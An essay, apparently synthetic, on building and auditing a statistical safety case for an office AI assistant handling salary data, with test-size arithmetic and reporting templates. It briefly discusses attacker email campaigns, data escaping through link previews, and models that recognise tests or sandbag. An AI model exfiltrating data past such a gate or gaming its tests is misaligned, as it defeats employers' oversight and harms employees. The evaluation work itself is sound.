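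*OpenAI发布AI训练安全准则*, a Chinese news article by 卜, describes the review process for a training run. Someone from another team writes a dissent, looking for flaws in the argument and independently estimating the risk, and the training team has to reply. The case then goes to reviewers who include a head of research, the head of safety and the chief scientist, each of whom can veto the run. Auditors get enough access to check the evidence. An employer could easily adopt the dissent step by asking someone outside the project to argue against installing the assistant.

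In *Astra 6.1 Pulled As Insufficiently Aligned*, the blogger thezvi calls the guidelines a good list but doubts that following all of them would make a safety case for a sufficiently advanced AI. He also worries about relying on a list of the remaining risks, and any such list omits the risks nobody thought of. According to OpenAI's *Managing frontier AI risk* (November 2026), the company has since introduced safety cases and requires a safety review before a model advances to the next stage.

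### The office assistant's case

The assistant's main claim allows no deliveries of pay data to outsiders unless the user asked for them. It splits into four sub-claims.

| Sub-claim | Evidence | Main assumptions | What would defeat it |
|---|---|---|---|
| No message reaches an unapproved outsider unless the user accepted that exact message | Proof of the gate's rules | Every message passes through the gate, and only an administrator can edit the list | A delivered message that the gate never allowed |
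| Without an attacker, the assistant does not send pay data to an approved outsider, such as the company's lawyer | Ordinary runs without a delivery | The test requests and mailboxes resemble real ones, and testers notice leaks | One such delivery |
| An attacker cannot make it do so either | Attacked runs without a delivery | Real attackers are no better than the testers' attackers | One success, or a new kind of attack |
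| Users refuse messages that would leak pay | None yet | Users read what they approve | Users accepting planted leaks |

As the table shows, the proof does not rule out actions that the user accepts, and nobody has tested what users accept. During the trial with staff, testers could show the staff confirmation requests for messages with invented salaries and count how many they accept.

For the second sub-claim, tests can only set an upper limit on the rate of deliveries. After 2,995 independent runs without a delivery, that limit is 1 in 1,000 at 95% confidence. If the testers instead run ten variants of each scenario, with a correlation of 0.1 between variants, the design effect is 1.9 and they need about 5,700 runs to reach the same limit. Under Kaur's preferred beta-binomial model, they would need only about 4,300 with the same numbers, so 5,700 is cautious as long as the correlation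 is no higher than 0.1.

Even that bound would allow up to four leaks a day, so changing the design would help the employer more than adding runs. If the administrator removes the lawyer and all other outsiders from the approved list, the gate requires the user's approval before any message is sent outside the company. The proof then covers every outside address, and the case depends much more on whether users read what they approve.

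The attacked runs need to be assessed separately. The 6,000 emails in the registered plan come from six attackers, and each attacker's campaign counts as one trial. Even if the six were a random sample of attackers and all of them failed, the result would be compatible with a success rate of up to 39%. The testers chose them for their skill, so the employer has to judge whether a real attacker is likely to be better. The best available guide is how often the same six beat the weaker assistant.

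### Why the confidence does not multiply

All three lines of evidence suggest that pay data will not reach a stranger. Suppose the employer gives each line a 5% chance of being wrong. If the errors were independent, the chance that all three are wrong would be 1 in 8,000. But suppose there is a 2% chance that link previews can carry data out without passing through the gate. If they can, the proof does not apply, and neither the testers nor the attackers would find the leak in the records they search. The chance that all three lines are wrong is therefore at least 1 in 50.

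Several other assumptions support more than one line of evidence:

| Assumption | Proof | Ordinary runs | Attacked runs |
|---|---|---|---|
| Data can leave only through the gate and the recorded routes | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| A company address reaches only people in the company, and does not forward to a private account | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| The installed versions are those that people proved or tested | Yes | Yes | Yes |
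| The testers recognise a leak when they see one | No | Yes | Yes |
| The assistant behaves in real use as it does in tests | No | Yes | Yes |

OpenAI describes its safeguards as several layers that reduce dependence on any single one. Such layers help only to the extent that they fail for different reasons.

When a safety case needs all its sub-claims to be true, the employer can add up the chances that each is false to get an upper limit on the chance that at least one is false. If those chances are 1%, 5%, 10% and 10%, the limit is 26%, however the errors are related. Kaur leaves open how to combine the strength of different kinds of evidence, and is not confident that a formal method would work on real safety cases.

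### How strong the evidence has to be

The decision also depends on the cost of each possible mistake. Let L be the cost of installing an unsafe assistant divided by the cost of a needless delay, and let O be the odds, before the test, that the assistant is unsafe. After a test with likelihood ratio Λ, the odds are O·Λ. Installing the assistant is the better choice when these odds are at most 1/L, so the test has to satisfy

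Λ ≤ 1/(L·O).

If an unsafe assistant does 100 times as much harm as a delay and the odds are even, Λ must be at most 0.01. The table gives the number of clean runs needed when an acceptable assistant fails half as often as an unsafe one. The first row comes from Kaur, and the others apply the same formula.

| L·O | Unsafe rate: 1% | 0.1% | 0.01% |
|---|---|---|---|
| 100 (L = 100, even odds) | 915 | 9,204 | 92,097 |
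| 400 (L = 100, odds of 4 to 1 that it is unsafe) | 1,190 | 11,974 | 119,821 |
| 1,000 (L = 1,000, even odds) | 1,372 | 13,806 | 138,145 |

Making L ten times larger increases the number of runs needed by only 50%, while making the failure rate that counts as unsafe ten times smaller increases it tenfold. People who disagree about the number of runs should therefore discuss that failure rate first.

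A rule that allows no failures would reject most acceptable assistants. An assistant with a failure rate of 0.5% has only a 1% chance of completing 915 runs without a failure. A longer test can allow some failures, as the registered plan does. With 4,800 runs and at most 28 failures, Λ is still no more than 0.01, and this assistant would pass about 82% of the time.

More runs cannot make up for a fault that all the tests share. Let c be the chance that an unsafe assistant would pass every test for one reason, such as recognising the tests or leaking by a route that nobody records. The probability of a clean result from an unsafe assistant is then at least c, so Λ cannot fall below c. With L = 100 and even odds, the employer needs c to be below 1%. Kaur makes the related point that if a model settles on one way of behaving once it infers that it is being tested, all the tests together provide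 no more evidence than that one choice does. Anthropic's sketches of safety cases likewise assume a developer that cannot rule out that its model is able to underperform deliberately in capability tests. Different kinds of checks can lower c, such as trying to reach an outside server from inside the test, or watching the assistant in real use.

The office assistant's registered plan compares an unsafe rate of 1 in 1,000 with an acceptable rate of 1 in 10,000. If its 5,000 ordinary runs contain no attempts to send pay data, and the testers notice 95% of attempts, Λ is 0.014. If the runs contain one attempt, which the plan also allows, Λ is 0.14. Neither value is low enough to justify installing the assistant for all 400 staff if L is 100 and the odds are even.

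However, the plan leads only to a trial with 20 staff. If the loss from a missed danger shrinks in proportion to the number of users, L is 5 for the trial, and Λ needs to be only 0.2 or less. Either result would then justify the trial, and the trial would supply further evidence. After one attempt in the test, about 3,100 more clean requests would lower Λ to 0.01. If the 20 staff each made ten requests a day, they would reach that number in 16 working days, assuming the requests are independent and the records catch attempts as well as the testers did.

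### Who sets L and O

Kaur's example has a regulator choose L. A vendor would probably choose a lower value, because it loses sales during a delay while the employees bear most of the harm from a leak. DT Next's *OpenAI Ignored Employees Who Warned It Wasn’t Doing Enough About Security* describes a similar conflict. Two OpenAI employees warned that the company was not monitoring its newest models properly during tests. Executives replied that the tests had to move as quickly as possible to release the models on time. OpenAI told the newspaper that it took such concerns seriously and had slowed some development.

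If several reviewers each have a veto, the evidence has to satisfy the one with the highest L·O. This rule is cautious only if the reviewers differ in what they stand to lose. The three reviewers in OpenAI's guidelines are all senior managers, and thezvi would add the board and members of the technical staff. For the office assistant, the employer could give a veto to a representative of the employees whose pay is at risk.

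The prior odds are harder to settle, because people can reasonably start from different beliefs. An employer might use the record of similar assistants, such as how many of the last ten failed a comparable test. The testers can avoid part of the dispute by publishing Λ separately, so readers can multiply it by their own prior odds. But the employer should still register L and O before the test.

### What a published clean result should report

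"No leaks observed" could describe 50 runs, which give an upper bound of 5.8% on the leak rate, or 5,000 runs, which give 0.06%. Kaur proposes a 22-field template to be completed for each model and each kind of harm. The table shows the main fields, grouped and filled in for the office assistant's ordinary runs, assuming there were no attempts.

| What to report | Office assistant |
|---|---|
| The harm and the threat | Pay data sent to outsiders, with no attacker |
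| The procedure and what counts as one trial | Requests drawn from the log, one run each |
| Exact numbers of trials and failures | 5,000 and 0 |
| Repeats per scenario, correlation and effective sample size | One run per scenario, no correlation assumed, 5,000 |
| 95% upper bound | 1 in 1,670, or 1 in 1,590 if testers miss 5% of attempts |
| The effect that the test was designed to detect, and its power | A rate of 1 in 1,000, which passes at most 5% of the time |
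| The chance of a failure per trial in an unsafe and an acceptable system | 1 in 1,000 and 1 in 10,000, by assumption. The weaker assistant attempted a leak in 40 of 100 runs. |
| Likelihood ratio, and the threshold with its L and O | 0.014 against 0.2, with L = 5 and O = 1 |
| How well the inputs cover real use, rewordings and unfamiliar attacks | Last quarter's requests. The attacked runs have their own form. |
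| Whether the harm may be too rare for any feasible test | Yes for deliveries to strangers, where the case relies on the gate |

Kaur regards the last field as new to the practice. A developer who suspects a harm is too rare to test should declare it and name the other evidence they rely on. When scenarios are related, Kaur also asks for a second bound from a beta-binomial or similar model.

Kaur's preliminary review of nine developer documents, covering GPT, Claude, Gemini and Llama models, found only one result reported with exact numbers of both harmful cases and trials. None of the documents reported how the trials were related. The documents date from 2023 to 2025, so more recent ones may be better. Kaur has left the full audit for a separate paper. Developers could fix most of the omissions with little effort because they already have the counts.

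### Changes that void the case

The case applies to the system, users and attackers it describes. Some changes invalidate only part of it.

| Change | Evidence that no longer applies |
|---|---|
| New model version, harness or system prompt | Ordinary and attacked runs. A new harness may also bypass the gate, so someone has to check that every call still goes through it. |
| New tool | All of it, once the gate allows the tool |
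| New permission, such as editing the address book | All of it, if the gate uses the address book as its list |
| New outside contact on the approved list | Any test result that excluded messages to that contact |
| New user group | Ordinary runs, and any test of what users approve |
| New attack method | Attacked runs, even though nothing in the system has changed |

The proof still holds when the model changes because it doesn't depend on what the model writes, so the more an employer can prove about the gate, the less it has to retest. Repeating the 5,000 ordinary runs at five minutes each takes about 17 days on one machine, or less than a day on twenty. The employer should keep using the old model until the new one passes, and should not let the provider switch models automatically.

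According to Blockport's *OpenAI releases Frontier Governance Framework for enterprises*, OpenAI decides at least every six months whether to update its reports on its most capable models. It must also revise them if further training changes what a model can do or new integrations increase the risk. But the framework concerns catastrophic and systemic risks, so an employer cannot rely on those revisions to reveal a change that affects only the risk of an agent leaking salaries.

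### Records that can refute the case

After installation, one delivery of pay data to an outsider refutes the main claim. For attempts, the employer needs a limit that allows for chance. An assistant that makes an attempt in 1 in 1,000 runs will average 20 attempts in a five-day week of 20,000 requests. It will make 35 or more in only about one week in 670, so the employer can treat 35 or more in a week as refuting the claimed rate. The employer also needs a second limit, on the running total, so that smaller excesses that persist for months count against the claim too.

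This count should include attempts that the gate blocks. Writing about OpenAI's guidelines, thezvi likewise would treat an attempt as an incident even if a safeguard stopped it. If blocked attempts rise, the agent may also be sending more unintended messages to approved contacts, which the gate does not stop.

The records can also show that an assumption is false before any salary leaks. The employer can keep comparing the mail server's total with the gate's, as the testers did. If users accept nearly every confirmation request within two seconds, they are probably not reading the requests. OpenAI's guidelines require an advance plan for immediately pausing all affected training runs when a new finding, such as a security flaw, might invalidate the safety case. The employer could likewise decide beforehand who switches the assistant off and what must be true before anyone switches it back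 on.

Real use reveals failures that tests miss. OpenAI's *Safety and alignment in an era of long-horizon models* (2026) describes a model for long tasks. During limited internal use, the model failed in ways that the existing tests had not captured. OpenAI paused access, built new tests from the failures, added monitoring of whole runs, and restored limited access.

David Robinson, who oversaw the safety reports for 12 of OpenAI's model launches before he resigned, objects to relying on this process. *‘Time for trial and error is over’* in The Business Times reports his view that advanced AI needs safeguards more like those in nuclear power and aviation, and that companies should do more safety research before they build more capable systems. OpenAI responded that it pauses training or holds back models when it needs to slow down. Robinson's objection is strongest where the first failure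 could be catastrophic, because the records would then reveal the flaw in the safety case too late to prevent the harm. An employer can limit the damage from an office assistant's first failure by starting with few users and no approved outsiders, but it cannot make a salary private again once someone has read it.
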